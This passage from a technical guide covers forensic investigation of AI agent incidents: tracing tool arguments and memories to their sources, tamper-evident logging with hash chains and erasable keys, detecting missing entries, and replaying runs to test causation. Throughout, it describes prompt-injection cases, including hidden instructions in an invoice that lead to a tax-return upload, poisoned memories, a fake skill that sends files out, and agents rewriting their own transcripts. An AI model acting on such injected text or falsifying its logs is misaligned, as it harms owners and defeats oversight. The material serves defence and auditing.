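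It then divides the tools that fetch information into trusted and untrusted ones. In an email program, the owner's contact list would be trusted, while incoming messages would not, because outsiders write them. For each argument, Agent-Sentry calculates an "untrusted hop depth", which is the longest chain of untrusted sources leading to the value. If S is the set of sources that the model named, then:

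depth(S) = the largest value, over all sources c in S, of
- 0, if c is trusted
- 1 + the largest depth among c's own arguments, if c is untrusted

An empty set has a depth of 0. Suppose the owner's request names the invoice folder, and the agent reads invoice 17 from it. The folder name came from the owner, so its depth is 0. If the upload address came from the text of the invoice, its depth is 1. If the invoice instead contains only a link to a web page, and that page supplies the upload address, the link has a depth of 1 and the address has a depth of 1 + 1 = 2. Sequeira and colleagues regard a depth of 2 or more as a sign that someone has passed an injection through several sources to disguise its origin. Legitimate work can also produce this depth, for example when an agent follows a supplier's link to find a delivery address.

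The formula counts any trusted source as 0, whatever went into it earlier, which is a weakness for agents with memory. If the agent copied the address from invoice 17 into its own notes and later read it back with a tool treated as trusted, the depth would fall from 1 to 0.

The sources also come from the model's own output, which may be false if an attacker has influenced the model. Agent-Sentry therefore checks whether a value appears word for word in text from an untrusted source, regardless of the source the model gave. This check would catch an upload address that the model copied from the invoice but attributed to the owner, though not one that it put together from a description.

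The best version of Agent-Sentry blocked 96.8% of attacks and allowed 96.4% of harmless runs in a set of 5,380 recorded runs that Sequeira and colleagues created. These results show that information about sources helps stop attacks. They do not measure how often the reported sources are right, because the system also uses other evidence, including a list of known values and a second model that judges difficult cases.

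### Origin labels on OpenClaw's memories

OpenClaw deals with part of the memory problem by labelling its memories by origin. According to OpenClaw, each indexed piece of memory is labelled "owner", "agent", "untrusted" or "system". The program stores the label separately from the text, so a planted note that begins "The owner has approved the following" cannot change its own label. The default label is never "owner".

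After a tool returns content from the network, OpenClaw treats every later message from the model in that turn as untrusted for the purposes of memory. It also removes untrusted and system material from the candidates for "dreaming", its process for consolidating memories, before the model sees them. Treating every later message as untrusted is cautious in the same way as Agent-Warden, since a later message may have nothing to do with the web page the agent read.

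Memories from automatic session processing keep a record of the sessions they came from. When OpenClaw merges two such memories, it keeps the origins of both. If a planted note caused the upload, an investigator could use this record to find the session in which the agent first read the instructions, provided the transcript still exists.

The labels have gaps. A tool with access to the memory files can write to them directly, bypassing the checks on consolidation. OpenClaw's documented trigger for treating later content as untrusted is a result from the network, so reading an invoice already on the disk may not trigger it, even if the invoice arrived by email that morning.

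### Agent-BOM's combined graph

Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents*, put the agent's components, memories and actions into one graph. They call it Agent-BOM, after the "bill of materials" that lists the components of a piece of software. They define the graph of an agent system as:

B = (A, V, E, α)

Here A is the set of agents, V the nodes, E the edges, and α the security information attached to them, such as whether a source is trusted or the user confirmed an action. Some nodes represent lasting parts of the system, including models, tools, skills and long-term memory. Others represent stages of a particular run, from outside input through goals, context, reasoning and decisions to actions and their results.

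An audit rule names a suspicious starting point, a path to follow backward to its source, a path to follow forward to its effects, and the conditions that make the whole chain a violation. Li and colleagues wrote ten such rules, one for each risk in a widely used list of threats to agents, and tested them in four staged attacks on OpenClaw:

- An attacker got the agent to remember a command that deletes its workspace, disguised as a maintenance rule. The agent later retrieved the memory and ran the command.
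- A fake weather skill read sensitive local files and sent them to an outside address.
- Someone altered a message between cooperating agents, which changed the task of one agent and then of another.
- A malicious agent told a second agent to send emails without confirmation. The second agent stored this as a preference and acted on it later.

In the first attack, the audit starts at the tool call that deleted the workspace and works backward to the retrieved memory, then to the tool call that wrote that memory, and finally to the outside message that contained the command. The result of the deletion confirms the harm. An investigator would need this kind of chain if an old note had caused the tax return to leak.

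Li and colleagues report that Agent-BOM reconstructed all four attacks. However, they staged the attacks themselves and knew which paths to look for, and they give no error rates for ordinary sessions. No standard test exists to fill this gap. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) surveyed 71 works on the subject in *From Agent Traces to Trust* and found no benchmark that evaluates a complete provenance chain.

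Agent-BOM also has to be in place before the incident, because its OpenClaw plugin records how the program assembles the context. Agent-BOM assumes that nobody has tampered with the plugin or the stored records.

A more basic difficulty is deciding how the graph should treat reasoning text. Agent-BOM draws edges from the context to the model's reasoning and from there to its decision. Sardianos and colleagues would keep the model's explanation as evidence but give it no causal edges, because such explanations often do not match what determined the behaviour. They also want software outside the agent to assign the source labels. To link text to actions, they would use overlap in wording only to choose which candidates to test first, and would establish a cause by rerunning the step without the suspected text.

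Wang and colleagues add that influence and justification are separate relations, because a false memory can cause an action without justifying it. In the invoice case, an edge from invoice 17 to the upload would mean that the invoice may have prompted the upload. Showing whether anything the owner wrote permitted the upload would require a different kind of edge.

### What exists for Windows and macOS

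Most of the tools that observe the operating system are for Linux, while many personal computers run Windows or macOS.

| Tool | What it links | Windows and macOS |
|---|---|---|
| AgentSight | Model messages to processes, files and connections | No, it requires Linux |
| Agent-Warden | Processes to files and their later readers | No, it requires Linux |
| ExecWeave | Tool calls to processes | Yes, but its developers measured it only on Linux |
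| Agent-Sentry | Tool arguments to their sources | Works inside the agent, tested only on recorded benchmark runs |
| OpenClaw's origin labels | Memories to their origins | Part of OpenClaw's own memory system |
| Agent-BOM | Inputs, memories, tools and actions | OpenClaw plugin, tested only on Ubuntu Linux |

Even on Linux, ExecWeave's portable collector cannot identify which process changed a file. It records only that the change happened during the session. A separate Linux collector can attribute file activity to processes.

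An investigator examining a Windows or macOS computer can make some of the same links by hand. For the `curl` upload, the investigator can follow the process tree from the network connection up to the agent program. The transcript should contain a tool call with the same command at nearly the same time, and a search of the earlier tool results may find the upload address in invoice 17. If two tool calls match the process equally well, the investigator should report both.

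## Protecting the record from alteration

Matching a transcript to processes on the machine is reliable only if nobody has edited either record. An agent that runs under its owner's account can usually edit every file the owner can, including its own transcript. In *Ring-0 by Default*, Li, Huang and colleagues (2026) found that two of the three coding agents they tested could rewrite their own transcripts. Most agents keep a plain JSON log, and *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) points out that a malicious skill or tool can overwrite it. An intruder with administrator rights can also reach the operating system's logs and any entries still in memory. Human intruders have long altered logs to hide their traces.

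Careful reading does not reliably reveal that a record has been altered. *Hearsay* (Dai, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested this by changing one detail in a copy of each of 115 agent records, then asking language models and people whether each record was genuine. One model flagged 49% of the altered copies and 5% of the originals. A second flagged 85% of the altered copies, but also 42% of the originals. Human readers, judging by majority in groups of three, flagged 37% of the altered copies and 10% of the originals.

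Most of the defences below make a log *tamper-evident*. They cannot stop someone from changing it, but a later check will reveal the change.

### Append-only files and hash chains

The simplest protection is storage that allows new entries but blocks changes to old ones. On Linux, an administrator can apply this restriction to a single file, and an agent running under an ordinary account cannot remove it, but another administrator can. Append-only storage does not suit every agent program. Two of the five that Dai and colleagues tested rewrite their whole record at every step, and OpenClaw's database has to change existing parts of its file.

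A *hash chain* is stronger because it ties each entry to all the earlier ones. It uses a hash function H, such as SHA-256, which turns data of any length into a 32-byte fingerprint. Nobody knows a practical way to find two inputs with the same SHA-256 fingerprint. If r(i) is the text of entry i, the chain stores this value with it:

h(i) = H(h(i−1) ‖ r(i))

The symbol ‖ means "followed by", and h(0) is a fixed starting value. Sharif's draft log format also chains its records. It specifies the order of fields and how numbers are written, because a stray space would change the hash.

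Suppose the invoice session produced the five entries below, and someone later replaces the third with "Lists the invoice folder". The hashes are invented and shortened to two characters.

| i | Original entry | Original h(i) | h(i) recalculated after the change |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads invoice 16 | a4 | a4 |
| 2 | Reads invoice 17 | 7c | 7c |
| 3 | Uploads the tax return | e1 | 5d |
| 4 | Reads invoice 18 | 09 | f2 |
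| 5 | Moves invoice 18 | b6 | 38 |

If the attacker changes only the text, the file still contains e1 for entry 3. An investigator who recalculates the chain gets 5d and knows something is wrong at that point. But the formula is public and needs no secret. An attacker who controls the whole file can therefore replace the last three hashes with 5d, f2 and 38, and the chain will pass every check.

Rewriting the chain fails only if someone has kept the original final value, b6, out of the attacker's reach. This value protects all five entries because an attacker has no practical way to change any of them and still produce b6. The owner could write it down or store it on another device. A timestamping service can also sign the value together with the current time, using a standard format that *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) describes. An attacker could have a rewritten chain timestamped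 too, but the new timestamp would show a later time.

An attacker can alter log entries until the computer sends out the next value. If it sends one every hour on the hour and the upload happens at 14:32, the attacker has until 15:00 to rewrite everything logged since 14:00, including the record of the upload.

### Keys that the logger erases

A secret key can protect entries before any value leaves the machine. The logger uses the key to compute a *message authentication code* (MAC), a tag that nobody can produce without that key. If the same key stays on the computer, however, an intruder who finds it can replace every tag. The logger therefore uses each key once:

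t(i) = MAC(K(i), r(i))
K(i+1) = F(K(i))

Here t(i) is the tag for entry i, and F is a function that is impractical to reverse. After computing the next key, the logger erases the old one. An intruder who takes over after entry 5 finds K(6) and can forge entries from then on, but cannot work back to K(3) to alter the upload. An auditor who kept K(1) on another machine can derive every key and check every tag.

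*Accountability of Things* (2023) credits the cryptographers Bellare and Yee with naming this property "forward integrity". *Runtime Verification for Trustworthy Computing* (2023) uses SealFS, a file system with this property, which can authenticate log data written after the computer starts and before an intruder gains elevated privileges.

Deletion from the end is harder to detect. If the attacker removes entries 4 and 5 along with their tags, the first three still pass. Zhao, Shoaib and colleagues (2025), in *Rethinking Tamper-Evident Logging*, address this in Nitro, a logging system for Linux that combines all the tags into one running total:

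T(i) = T(i−1) ⊕ MAC(K(i), r(i))

The symbol ⊕ combines two values bit by bit, and anyone who has the result and one of the values can recover the other. To hide the loss of entries 4 and 5, the attacker would need T(3). The computer now holds only T(5), and removing the last two tags from it would require the erased keys K(4) and K(5). An earlier system, KennyLoggings, left old tags readable on the disk, so an attacker could put one back. Nitro occasionally saves a tag but encrypts it. The saved tags also help an auditor determine how much of an altered log is still genuine.

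An intruder might also gain control before the logger has tagged the entry that records the break-in. Many loggers queue events and process them a moment later, and attackers have exploited that delay. Nitro tags each event inside the kernel as it happens and replaces the key immediately. An agent without administrator rights normally cannot read the kernel's memory, so it would have to gain higher privileges before it could read even the current key.

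### Signatures and hash trees

Anyone who can check a MAC can also forge one, because both tasks need the same secret. This is a problem if the owner wants to show the log to an insurer or a court. With a digital signature, the logger signs with a private key and anyone can check the signature with the matching public key. This is why signatures rank above hash chains on the integrity scale of Nian and colleagues.

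A signature is only as trustworthy as the control over its private key. In Sharif's draft, signatures are optional and made with the agent's own key, so a compromised agent that can use the key could sign a rewritten log. The key is safer in a separate program that the agent cannot control.

Signing every entry also lets an investigator prove one entry without showing the rest. A *hash tree*, or Merkle tree, does the same with a single signed or published value for the whole log. It hashes the entries individually, then hashes the results in pairs, then pairs those results, until one value remains. For four entries with hashes a, b, c and d:

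root = H(H(a ‖ b) ‖ H(c ‖ d))

To prove that the third entry belongs to the log, the investigator supplies the entry, the hash d and the combined hash H(a ‖ b). The other party can then calculate the root and compare it with the published value. Doubling the log adds one hash to the proof. A log of a million entries has 20 levels, because 2²⁰ is 1,048,576, so the proof contains 20 hashes of 32 bytes each, or 640 bytes. With a plain hash chain, the other party would also need every later entry.

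Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner (2026), in *Agent Flight Recorder*, combine both structures. Their recorder chains an agent's actions, groups them into batches and builds a tree for each. If M(t) is the root for batch t, the recorder publishes:

R(t) = H(M(t) ‖ R(t−1))

If someone deletes a whole batch, the next published value no longer fits the one before it. The recorder publishes these values on a public blockchain, but its developers say that a hash chain in write-once storage is enough for an internal audit, and that a timestamping service may be cheaper and simpler for parties who already agree on whom to trust. A blockchain is useful when the parties have no such agreement. An owner who only wants to guard against their own agent probably does not need a blockchain.

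### Where the log can live

These methods work better if the agent cannot access the log or its keys. The options differ in whom the owner has to trust and how soon an entry is safe from alteration.

| Location | What the owner must trust | When an entry is safe |
|---|---|---|
| Another user account | The operating system and everyone with administrator rights | Once a program in that account has written it |
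| Protected system service | The kernel, until an intruder controls it | Nitro tags it at once, but may hold it in memory for about a second |
| Secure hardware | The maker of the chip and the software that feeds it | Once the hardware has signed or stored it |
| Second device | The device and its connection to the computer | For critical events in the HardLog system, as they happen |
| Remote server | The server's operator and whoever can delete its data | On arrival, so not while the computer is offline |

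The simplest option is to run a small logging program under a separate user account. The agent program passes each entry to the logging program, and only the logging program can write to the file. This prevents the agent from revising old entries, though it can still submit false ones.

An intruder who gains control of the kernel can't convincingly alter earlier entries recorded by a system service such as Nitro, but can still erase them from the disk. Separate hardware can prevent this. HardLog and a similar system, OmniLog, each send events to a small circuit board with storage that the computer cannot overwrite. Other systems use Intel SGX, a protected area inside some processors, to shield the log from privileged software. An outsider also needs proof that the computer is still using the secure hardware, and *Runtime Verification for Trustworthy Computing* suggests getting it through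 a remote check.

A remote server is the most familiar place to keep the log, and it protects against the loss of the whole computer. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a system that authorises agents' actions from outside the computer they run on and keeps a hash chain that remains valid even after someone clears the encrypted contents of old entries. However, if the owner's computer has a saved password that allows deletion on the server, the agent may be able to use it. The computer should therefore have permission to add entries but not to change or delete them. An attacker on the computer can still block entries before they are sent, and the server cannot recover them.

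### What an intact log does not prove

Dai and colleagues added a hash chain to the record of the coding agent Aider and then made the agent program write false records. In 14 runs, the program left out the model's reply, and in another 14 it added a sentence the model had never written. The chain passed its check in all 28 runs because the records were already false when the program hashed them.

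Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, gives a short proof that better cryptography cannot solve the problem of missing entries. Suppose someone claims that the owner approved every upload, and consider two possible histories:

1. The agent made two uploads, both with approval, and logged both.
2. The agent made the same two uploads and a third without approval, and left the third out of the log.

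The log is identical in both histories, so any method that uses only the log must produce the same result for both. A method that confirms the claim is therefore wrong in the second history. Signatures and outside copies of the latest hash don't help, because they cover the same two entries. Only a record that the agent does not control, and that would have included the third upload, can support the claim.

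Disproving the claim takes less evidence. One authenticated upload is enough if a complete and independent record of approvals contains no approval for it.

An accurate entry can also mislead, as a signed log of the email requests in the postmark-mcp case would have done.

Omissions also happen without an attacker. Dai and colleagues ran the unmodified coding agent SWE-agent and found that its records lacked some of the model's tool calls in 19 of 28 runs. SWE-agent accepts only one tool call at a time. When the model sent several, SWE-agent rejected the message and saved neither the message nor the rejection, so the remaining record looked complete.

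### Finding gaps

*Sequence numbers* reveal some missing entries. If a log goes from 347 to 349, entry 348 is missing. An attacker who can rewrite the log can renumber it, so the numbers need the same protection as the text. Sequence numbers also don't reveal events that were never numbered or entries missing from the end. To detect missing entries at the end, Sharif recommends closing each session with a record that contains a hash of the whole session. If the closing record is missing, the program may have crashed or someone may have cut the log short. After a crash, the program must add an entry that documents the gap.

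A *heartbeat* is an entry that the logger writes at regular intervals even when nothing happens. Suppose the logger sends one to a server every minute, each containing the latest sequence number. If one heartbeat arrives at 14:31 and the next at 14:50, the investigator knows which 19 minutes to examine. The laptop may have been asleep, which the operating system's power records could confirm. If the last heartbeat before the gap contained the number 347 but the server holds only 340 entries, seven failed to arrive or later disappeared. But a compromised agent program could keep sending heartbeats while leaving a single upload out of the log.

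Finding that kind of omission requires a second, independent source. In Zhao's hypothetical example, an agent's signed log passes every check and lists three emails with attachments, but the company's mail gateway recorded four. Comparing the two reveals the extra email but not who sent it. The agent may have bypassed its log, the log may have lost an entry, or a person may have used the same account.

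Dai and colleagues built a system that keeps a second record of what a coding agent does, and measured how well it works. One part sits between the agent program and the model and copies every request and reply. The other records each process that starts and each file that changes. A script then compares this outside record with the agent program's own and looks for items that appear in only one of them.

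The team finalized the rules before testing the script on 66 altered records and 84 genuine ones. The script detected 64 of the alterations. It reported no fabricated text in the genuine records, and the omissions it reported in 15 of them were tool calls that SWE-agent had in fact dropped. In an earlier test, the script caught 109 of 115 alterations, but it also flagged 37 of 115 genuine records until the team added more exceptions to the rules.

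The team then gave a language model the rules and asked it to add fabrications that the script would miss. The script caught all 65 attempts that used newly written text but missed all 35 that reused a genuine sentence from the same record. After a one-line repair, it caught all 50 attempts in the second round but also flagged 2 of 21 genuine records from one agent program.

A malicious program could also give the model false text, which would then appear in the copied traffic. In one experiment, a program changed a failed software test result to a success before passing it to the model. The record of processes revealed the change in all 11 runs where it occurred, because it included the failing process's exit code. It would not have revealed a change to the wording of a tool's output that left the exit code the same.

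Dai and colleagues recorded coding tasks of at most seven minutes, in an environment where the agent program could reach the model only through the recorder. Someone running an agent on a home computer would need a similar arrangement, or the agent program could bypass the recorder. The model's provider may also have a copy of the model calls. Dai and colleagues retrieved the provider's copies of 708 calls, and every one matched their own record exactly.

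Figuera (2026), in *Notarized Agents*, proposes that a service sign a receipt for each call it receives from an agent, encrypt the receipt so that only the agent's owner can read it, and publish it in a public log. If a mail provider did this, the owner would learn of any emails missing from the transcript. Receipts would not cover an upload to the attacker's own site, and neither would the linked records that Kühlewind and Birkholz propose.

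### What protection costs

Hashing takes little time or storage. The recorder by Bindschaedler and colleagues added a median of 48 microseconds and 512 bytes per event. For an agent that makes 200 tool calls a day, that comes to about a hundredth of a second and 0.1 MB a day.

Publishing the values in batches of 100 events cost $2.30 per 100,000 events, or about 0.23 cents per batch. The same agent would fill only two batches a day, so an entry could go unprotected for many hours. Publishing every hour around the clock would shorten that gap and cost about $20 a year. The developers measured the transaction cost on a test network, and real fees vary.

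Recording everything the operating system does is more demanding. Zhao and colleagues tested Nitro against QuickLog2, an earlier tamper-evident logger, on virtual machines with 36 processor cores. QuickLog2 increased processor time by 15.9% to 895.1%. Nitro's overhead was 10 to 25 times lower under heavy load and 2 to 10 times lower with ordinary programs such as Firefox. An overloaded logger can also drop entries, which leaves an investigator with the same gaps as if an attacker had deleted them. Under heavy load, QuickLog2 lost 31% to 98% of its entries, while Nitro lost at most 2.2%.

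Nitro used about 345 MB of ordinary memory, which is noticeable on a small laptop, and reserved up to 65 MB more in the kernel. It runs only on Linux. Its developers think a Windows version is feasible, but it would have to capture events differently, and Windows gives outside developers less access to its kernel.

The main drawback of a second record is the disk space it uses. In the tests by Dai and colleagues, it needed to be only 1.08 times the size of the agent program's own record. Their recorder took up 2.78 times as much space because some agent programs rewrite their whole record at every step, and it kept every version.

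## Replaying the agent's run

An intact record shows what the agent did on one occasion. It may not show whether the agent would have uploaded the tax return without the hidden text in invoice 17. An investigator can look into this by replaying the session, but "replay" can refer to four procedures, which need different saved material.

| Kind of replay | What must have been saved | What it can show |
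|---|---|---|
| Displaying the transcript | The transcript | The order of messages, tool calls and results |
| Re-running the agent program with recorded responses | Model responses, tool results, and the program's version, settings and memory files | How the program handled each response |
| Sending the context to the model again | The exact context, the model's version and its settings | How often the model makes the same choice |
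| Reproducing the machine's execution | Every outside input to the recorded programs, and its timing | What each program did, including scripts such as `tidy.py` |

A transcript viewer makes a long session easier to follow, but it adds no evidence. If the transcript has gaps or false entries, the display will have them too.

### Re-running the agent program

To re-run the agent program, the investigator starts the same version in an isolated copy of the owner's system and replaces the model with a stand-in. The stand-in answers each of the program's requests with the saved response. A second stand-in can return the saved tool results, so that no command runs. This method works even after the provider has withdrawn the model.

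In the invoice case, such a rerun could show whether the program's settings would have triggered an approval prompt before the upload. It might also rebuild a context that the program never saved, if the memory files are unchanged. It cannot show whether the model would choose the upload again, because the rerun takes that choice from the recording.

The investigator can also execute the tool calls again in a restored environment to see their effects. Liu and Lu (2026), in *Replay Fidelity in LLM Agent Evaluation*, measured how faithful such reruns are. They reran the recorded code from 71 failed agent runs in AppWorld, a simulated set of everyday apps, without calling a model. They then compared the printed output, databases and test results with the originals. With the documented settings, 42 runs matched. When they also reset the random number generator before each step, 68 matched.

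Most of the mismatches were minor. Of the 29 runs that failed to match at first, 25 differed in text about when a login token expired, and 24 of those ended with the same data and test results as the original. The other four of the 29 ended with different data, including different password-reset codes.

A rerun can also pass all these checks and still differ in a way that matters later. In one case, two reruns of the same session both passed, although one had received the same token at every login and the other had received 20 different tokens. Liu and Lu then ran a short program that logged out and tried to use the earliest token. Logging out had cancelled the token in the first rerun, but in the second the old token still worked and the program created a playlist.

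Restoring a saved snapshot has the same weakness. Pakhomov and Nijkamp (2026), in *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual*, saved a test environment at 24 points and continued from each with a fixed script in place of the model. The environment's tools failed at random, in 5% of calls in one test and 20% in another. The restored copies had the same fingerprint as the saved state and always matched one another, but they diverged from the original run at 9 of the 24 points in the 5% test and at 20 of the 24 in the 20% test.

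The snapshot had left out the program's position in its sequence of random numbers. Once Pakhomov and Nijkamp saved and restored that position, the differences disappeared. An investigator should therefore compare a restored run with the original record, not just with other restored copies. Comparing only the outcomes is not enough, because the final test result was the same in every case.

### Recording the whole machine

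A recording of the machine's execution can show what `tidy.py` did inside Python. Nothing described so far can do that unless the script still exists and behaves as it did before. A processor that starts from the same state and receives the same inputs gives the same results, so the recorder doesn't have to save every instruction. It saves what can vary, such as data from the network, the results the operating system returned to programs and the exact moments when it interrupted them. During replay, the computer runs the same instructions again and receives the saved inputs at the same points.

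Replay is older than AI agents. *ReVirt* (Dunlap, King and colleagues, 2002) ran the whole operating system in a virtual machine and recorded it from outside, which made it possible to replay an attack even if the intruder had replaced the operating system.

In *Eidetic Systems* (2014), Devecsery, Chow and colleagues describe Arnold, a recorder they built for Linux workstations and used on their own machines for two to four weeks. It recorded nearly everything they did. At the rates they measured, a 4 TB drive would hold 4 to 14 years of recordings. Three weeks, enough to cover the invoice case, would take up at most about 55 GB.

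*Engineering Record And Replay For Deployability* (O'Callahan, Jones and colleagues, 2017) describes rr, a tool developers use to find bugs. The tool records a chosen group of processes and, unlike Arnold, needs no changes to the Linux kernel.

| System | Slowdown while recording | Storage |
|---|---|---|
| ReVirt | 0–8% for logging; virtualisation adds 13–58% on work that uses the kernel heavily | Several months on one disk |
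| Arnold | Under 12% on all but two tests with one disk; downloading a large code repository took about twice as long | 0.8–2.6 GB a day |
| rr | 49–79% on four tests; a parallel software build took 7.85 times as long | 0.08–19 MB a second, plus copies of some files |

Arnold's main advantage is that nobody has to decide in advance which fields to log. In one demonstration, a user wanted to know how a wrong citation had got into a paper. Arnold re-executed the programs involved and traced the data back through several of them to the web page the user had been reading. The query took 209 seconds.

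Devecsery and colleagues also used Arnold to find out which data a test server had leaked through the 2014 Heartbleed flaw. Their method works on sessions recorded before anyone knew about the flaw. In the invoice case, a similar query could start from the tax return and follow its contents through Python to the network, even though Python encrypted them before sending them.

None of these systems is ready for an ordinary owner's computer. Arnold needs a modified Linux kernel and covers only one machine. rr runs one thread at a time, which is why the parallel build was so slow. O'Callahan and colleagues also assume that the recorded program is not hostile. A malicious program that knew about rr could use it to escape from a sandbox, so rr is a risky choice for recording a compromised agent.

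rr still requires Linux, although it now supports some ARM processors, including Apple's M-series, which the 2017 paper had ruled out. Graphics processors are another difficulty. Undo, a commercial recorder, does not support programs that use one common route to GPU acceleration, and many people who run a model on their own computer use a GPU.

If the model runs on a provider's servers, its responses reach the owner's computer as network data, so a whole-machine recording can reproduce the invoice session exactly without contacting the provider. But the recording can't show what would have happened without the hidden text, because the model would have to generate a new response to the changed context.

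### Why the model may answer differently

The investigator gets a new response by sending the model the context from just before the upload, then checks whether it requests the upload again. No tool has to run if the upload was the next call, but if the agent first listed a folder and opened the tax return, the investigator has to let the run continue through those steps. The saved tool results can be reused only while the model makes the same calls as before. Any different call has to run on a restored copy of the owner's files.

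An agent may act differently when its run is replayed. Gruber and Hilgert repeatedly gave OpenClaw the same request for a reminder, keeping every condition they could control the same. In some runs it created a scheduled task, and in others it edited `HEARTBEAT.md`, a file of jobs that the agent checks periodically. An investigator who finds no scheduled task therefore cannot conclude that the owner never asked for a reminder. Configuration files and folder layouts stayed the same across the runs.

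Part of the variation comes from *sampling*. A model gives each possible next token a probability, and the software normally picks one at random according to those probabilities. A setting called *temperature* controls how random this choice is, and at 0 the software picks the most probable token.

Even at temperature 0, a hosted model's output can vary because computers round their results, so the order of additions matters. In standard arithmetic on most computers, (0.1 + 0.2) + 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, while 0.1 + (0.2 + 0.3) gives 0.6. A provider processes several customers' requests together in a batch, and the batch size can change the order in which the hardware adds numbers. If two tokens are almost equally probable, a tiny difference can change which one the software picks, and the rest of the response may then differ. *Causal Agent Replay* (Shah, 2026) gives this explanation,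 citing 2025 work by the AI company Thinking Machines Lab, and notes that some current models may not accept a temperature setting.

The agent's inputs change too. Its memory files may contain new notes, a web page it read may have changed or disappeared, and the agent program may put the current date into the context. Saved copies solve most of these problems, but they don't help if the provider has retired the model. A newer model may refuse to follow the hidden instructions that its predecessor followed, but that would be weak evidence about the original session.

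### Deterministic inference

Engineers can remove the numerical variation by making the software add numbers in the same order whatever the batch size. Running one request at a time also avoids the effect of batching. Shah found that a local model run this way with a fixed *seed*, the starting value for its random choices, gave exactly the same output each time.

Pakhomov and Nijkamp repeated 34 calls on a server they controlled, and all gave identical output. They also sent identical requests with the same seed to a hosted model, and none of the four calls they could compare reproduced the earlier output. They conclude that exact replay may be unavailable for hosted models, though four calls are very few and the service may have ignored the seed. Yun, Kim and colleagues (2026) also warn in *Correct Answers, Unsupported Findings* that a temperature of 0 and a fixed seed do not guarantee identical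 output from a hosted service.

Exact replay is therefore realistic when the owner runs an open-weight model on their own computer. With a hosted model, the investigator should resend several saved requests and measure how often the responses match.

A removal test is more informative when it compares how often the upload occurs across many runs with the hidden text and many without it. It doesn't need exact replay, which reproduces only one of the responses the model could have given. Removing the hidden text might also change that response just because the context is different.

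### Testing with the suspect text removed

For the invoice case, such a test could work as follows:

1. The investigator restores the environment to the moment before the agent read invoice 17.
2. The agent completes the task 20 times with the original invoice.
3. It completes the task another 20 times with a version in which harmless text of about the same length replaces the hidden instructions.
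4. The investigator counts the uploads in each set of runs.

The replay's starting point matters because the text in the invoice influences the agent's later files and messages. If the agent has already written `tidy.py`, cleaning the invoice does not remove the script from the disk. The model's own messages may also repeat the plan, and the investigator cannot edit Codex's encrypted reasoning. Pakhomov and Nijkamp similarly warn against pairing a cleaned history with an environment that the error has already changed.

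Replacing the text is better than deleting it, because deletion also shortens the context. The investigator could also keep the words but change who appears to have written them. Pakhomov and Nijkamp describe an experiment by another team that moved wrong claims from models' own earlier reasoning to messages from users, tools or memory. The wording stayed the same, but models openly corrected the claims 23 to 93 percentage points more often after the move.

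The runs with the original invoice are necessary because a second attempt can turn out differently by chance. *ReplayRCA* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) cites a set of failed agent runs in which retrying without any correction fixed 6.9%, so a single clean rerun after removing the text would prove little.

Suppose the upload occurs in 14 of the 20 runs with the hidden text and in none of the 20 without it. If the text made no difference, the 14 uploads would be spread at random over all 40 runs. The chance that every one of them would fall among the 20 runs with the text is:

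p = C(20, 14) / C(40, 14) = 38,760 / 23,206,929,840 ≈ 0.0000017

C(n, k) is the number of ways to choose k items from n. This calculation is a one-sided Fisher's exact test, and the result is strong evidence that the text makes the upload more likely.

It is weaker evidence that the upload never happens without the text. If q is the true rate without it, the chance of seeing no upload in 20 runs is (1 − q)²⁰. Setting this to 5% gives the usual upper limit:

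(1 − q)²⁰ = 0.05, so q ≈ 0.14

Zero uploads in 20 runs is still compatible with a true upload rate of up to about 14%. To bring that limit below 1%, the investigator would need 299 runs without an upload.

Even at that limit, the text would be the likely cause of the original upload. If the true upload rates were 70% with the text and 14% without it, at least four in five of the uploads in runs with the text would not have happened if the text had been absent. This assumes that the replay matches the original session in every other relevant way.

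The test also depends on the harmful action happening again. Yun and colleagues tried a removal test on one incident from a simulated bank, running the agent twice with the suspect text and twice without it. The incident did not recur in any of the four runs, so they could not tell whether the text had an effect. With only two runs per condition, a true rate of up to about 78% is compatible with seeing no recurrence, so the result does not rule out the text as a cause.

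More runs help, but an attack that rarely works requires many runs to detect. If the agent follows the hidden instructions in one run out of 20, there is a 36% chance that 20 runs will include no uploads. Five uploads in 100 runs with the hidden instructions and none in 100 without them would give p ≈ 0.03, which is modest evidence from 200 runs.

An action may also depend on two texts together. Suppose invoice 17 contains the upload address and a planted memory note tells the agent to obey instructions in invoices. Removing either one prevents the upload, so each looks fully responsible. For steps in a run, Shah divides responsibility using the *Shapley value*, which averages how much each factor adds over every order in which the factors could appear. In this example, the first text adds nothing and the second adds the whole effect, whichever order they appear in, so the invoice and the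 note each get half the responsibility. In a synthetic test with two equally responsible steps, Shah's software gave them 0.44 and 0.45.

### Finding the step that decided the outcome

Replay can also help show when the agent turned to the attacker's task. Shah's software, Causal Agent Replay, keeps everything before a chosen step unchanged, has the agent continue from there many times, and reports how often the harmful outcome recurs. In Shah's example, a support agent reads a message with hidden instructions and issues a refund. The agent decides to issue the refund one step before it makes the call that issues it.

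Rerunning from an early, harmless step can make that step seem to matter, because the agent also gets a new chance at every later step. Shah therefore looks for the latest step from which a rerun still clearly changes the outcome. In the invoice case, the agent might avoid the upload in 30% of reruns that start just after it read invoice 17, but in almost none that start after it had written its plan. The agent would then have decided to upload somewhere between those two points. Shah has validated the method only on synthetic cases, and the demonstrations use simulated tools.

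Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *AgenTracer*, used a different kind of replay to label failures in systems of several cooperating agents. A language model that knows the right answer goes through a failed run from the beginning and proposes a correction for each step. The system then makes that correction and re-runs everything after it. The decisive error is the earliest step whose correction turns failure into success:

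t* = the smallest t for which Ω(R(τ, t, a′)) = 1

Here τ is the failed run, a′ the corrected action at step t, R the rerun with that correction, and Ω the result, 1 for success and 0 for failure. AgenTracer stops at the first correction that works, so it can identify the wrong step as the cause of the failure if the rerun succeeded by chance.

The team also planted errors in successful runs, which gave them more than 2,000 labelled failures in total. They used these to train a small model to find the decisive error from the log alone. The model identified the exact step in 20.7% of handmade test cases. On automatically generated cases, it reached 37.3% when it did not have the correct answer to the task, slightly below Claude Sonnet 4, a general-purpose model from 2025, at 38.8%. It is therefore better to use a model's reading of a log to choose which steps to test than to treat it as a finding.

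Canale and Soulis test newer models and make an allowance for chance. They restore a simulated online shop's office system by repeating every recorded action and checking that each result matches the original byte for byte. A model then proposes one replacement action, and the original agent continues five times from there. For comparison, the agent also continues five times from its own original action:

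causal repair = success rate with the new action − success rate with the original action

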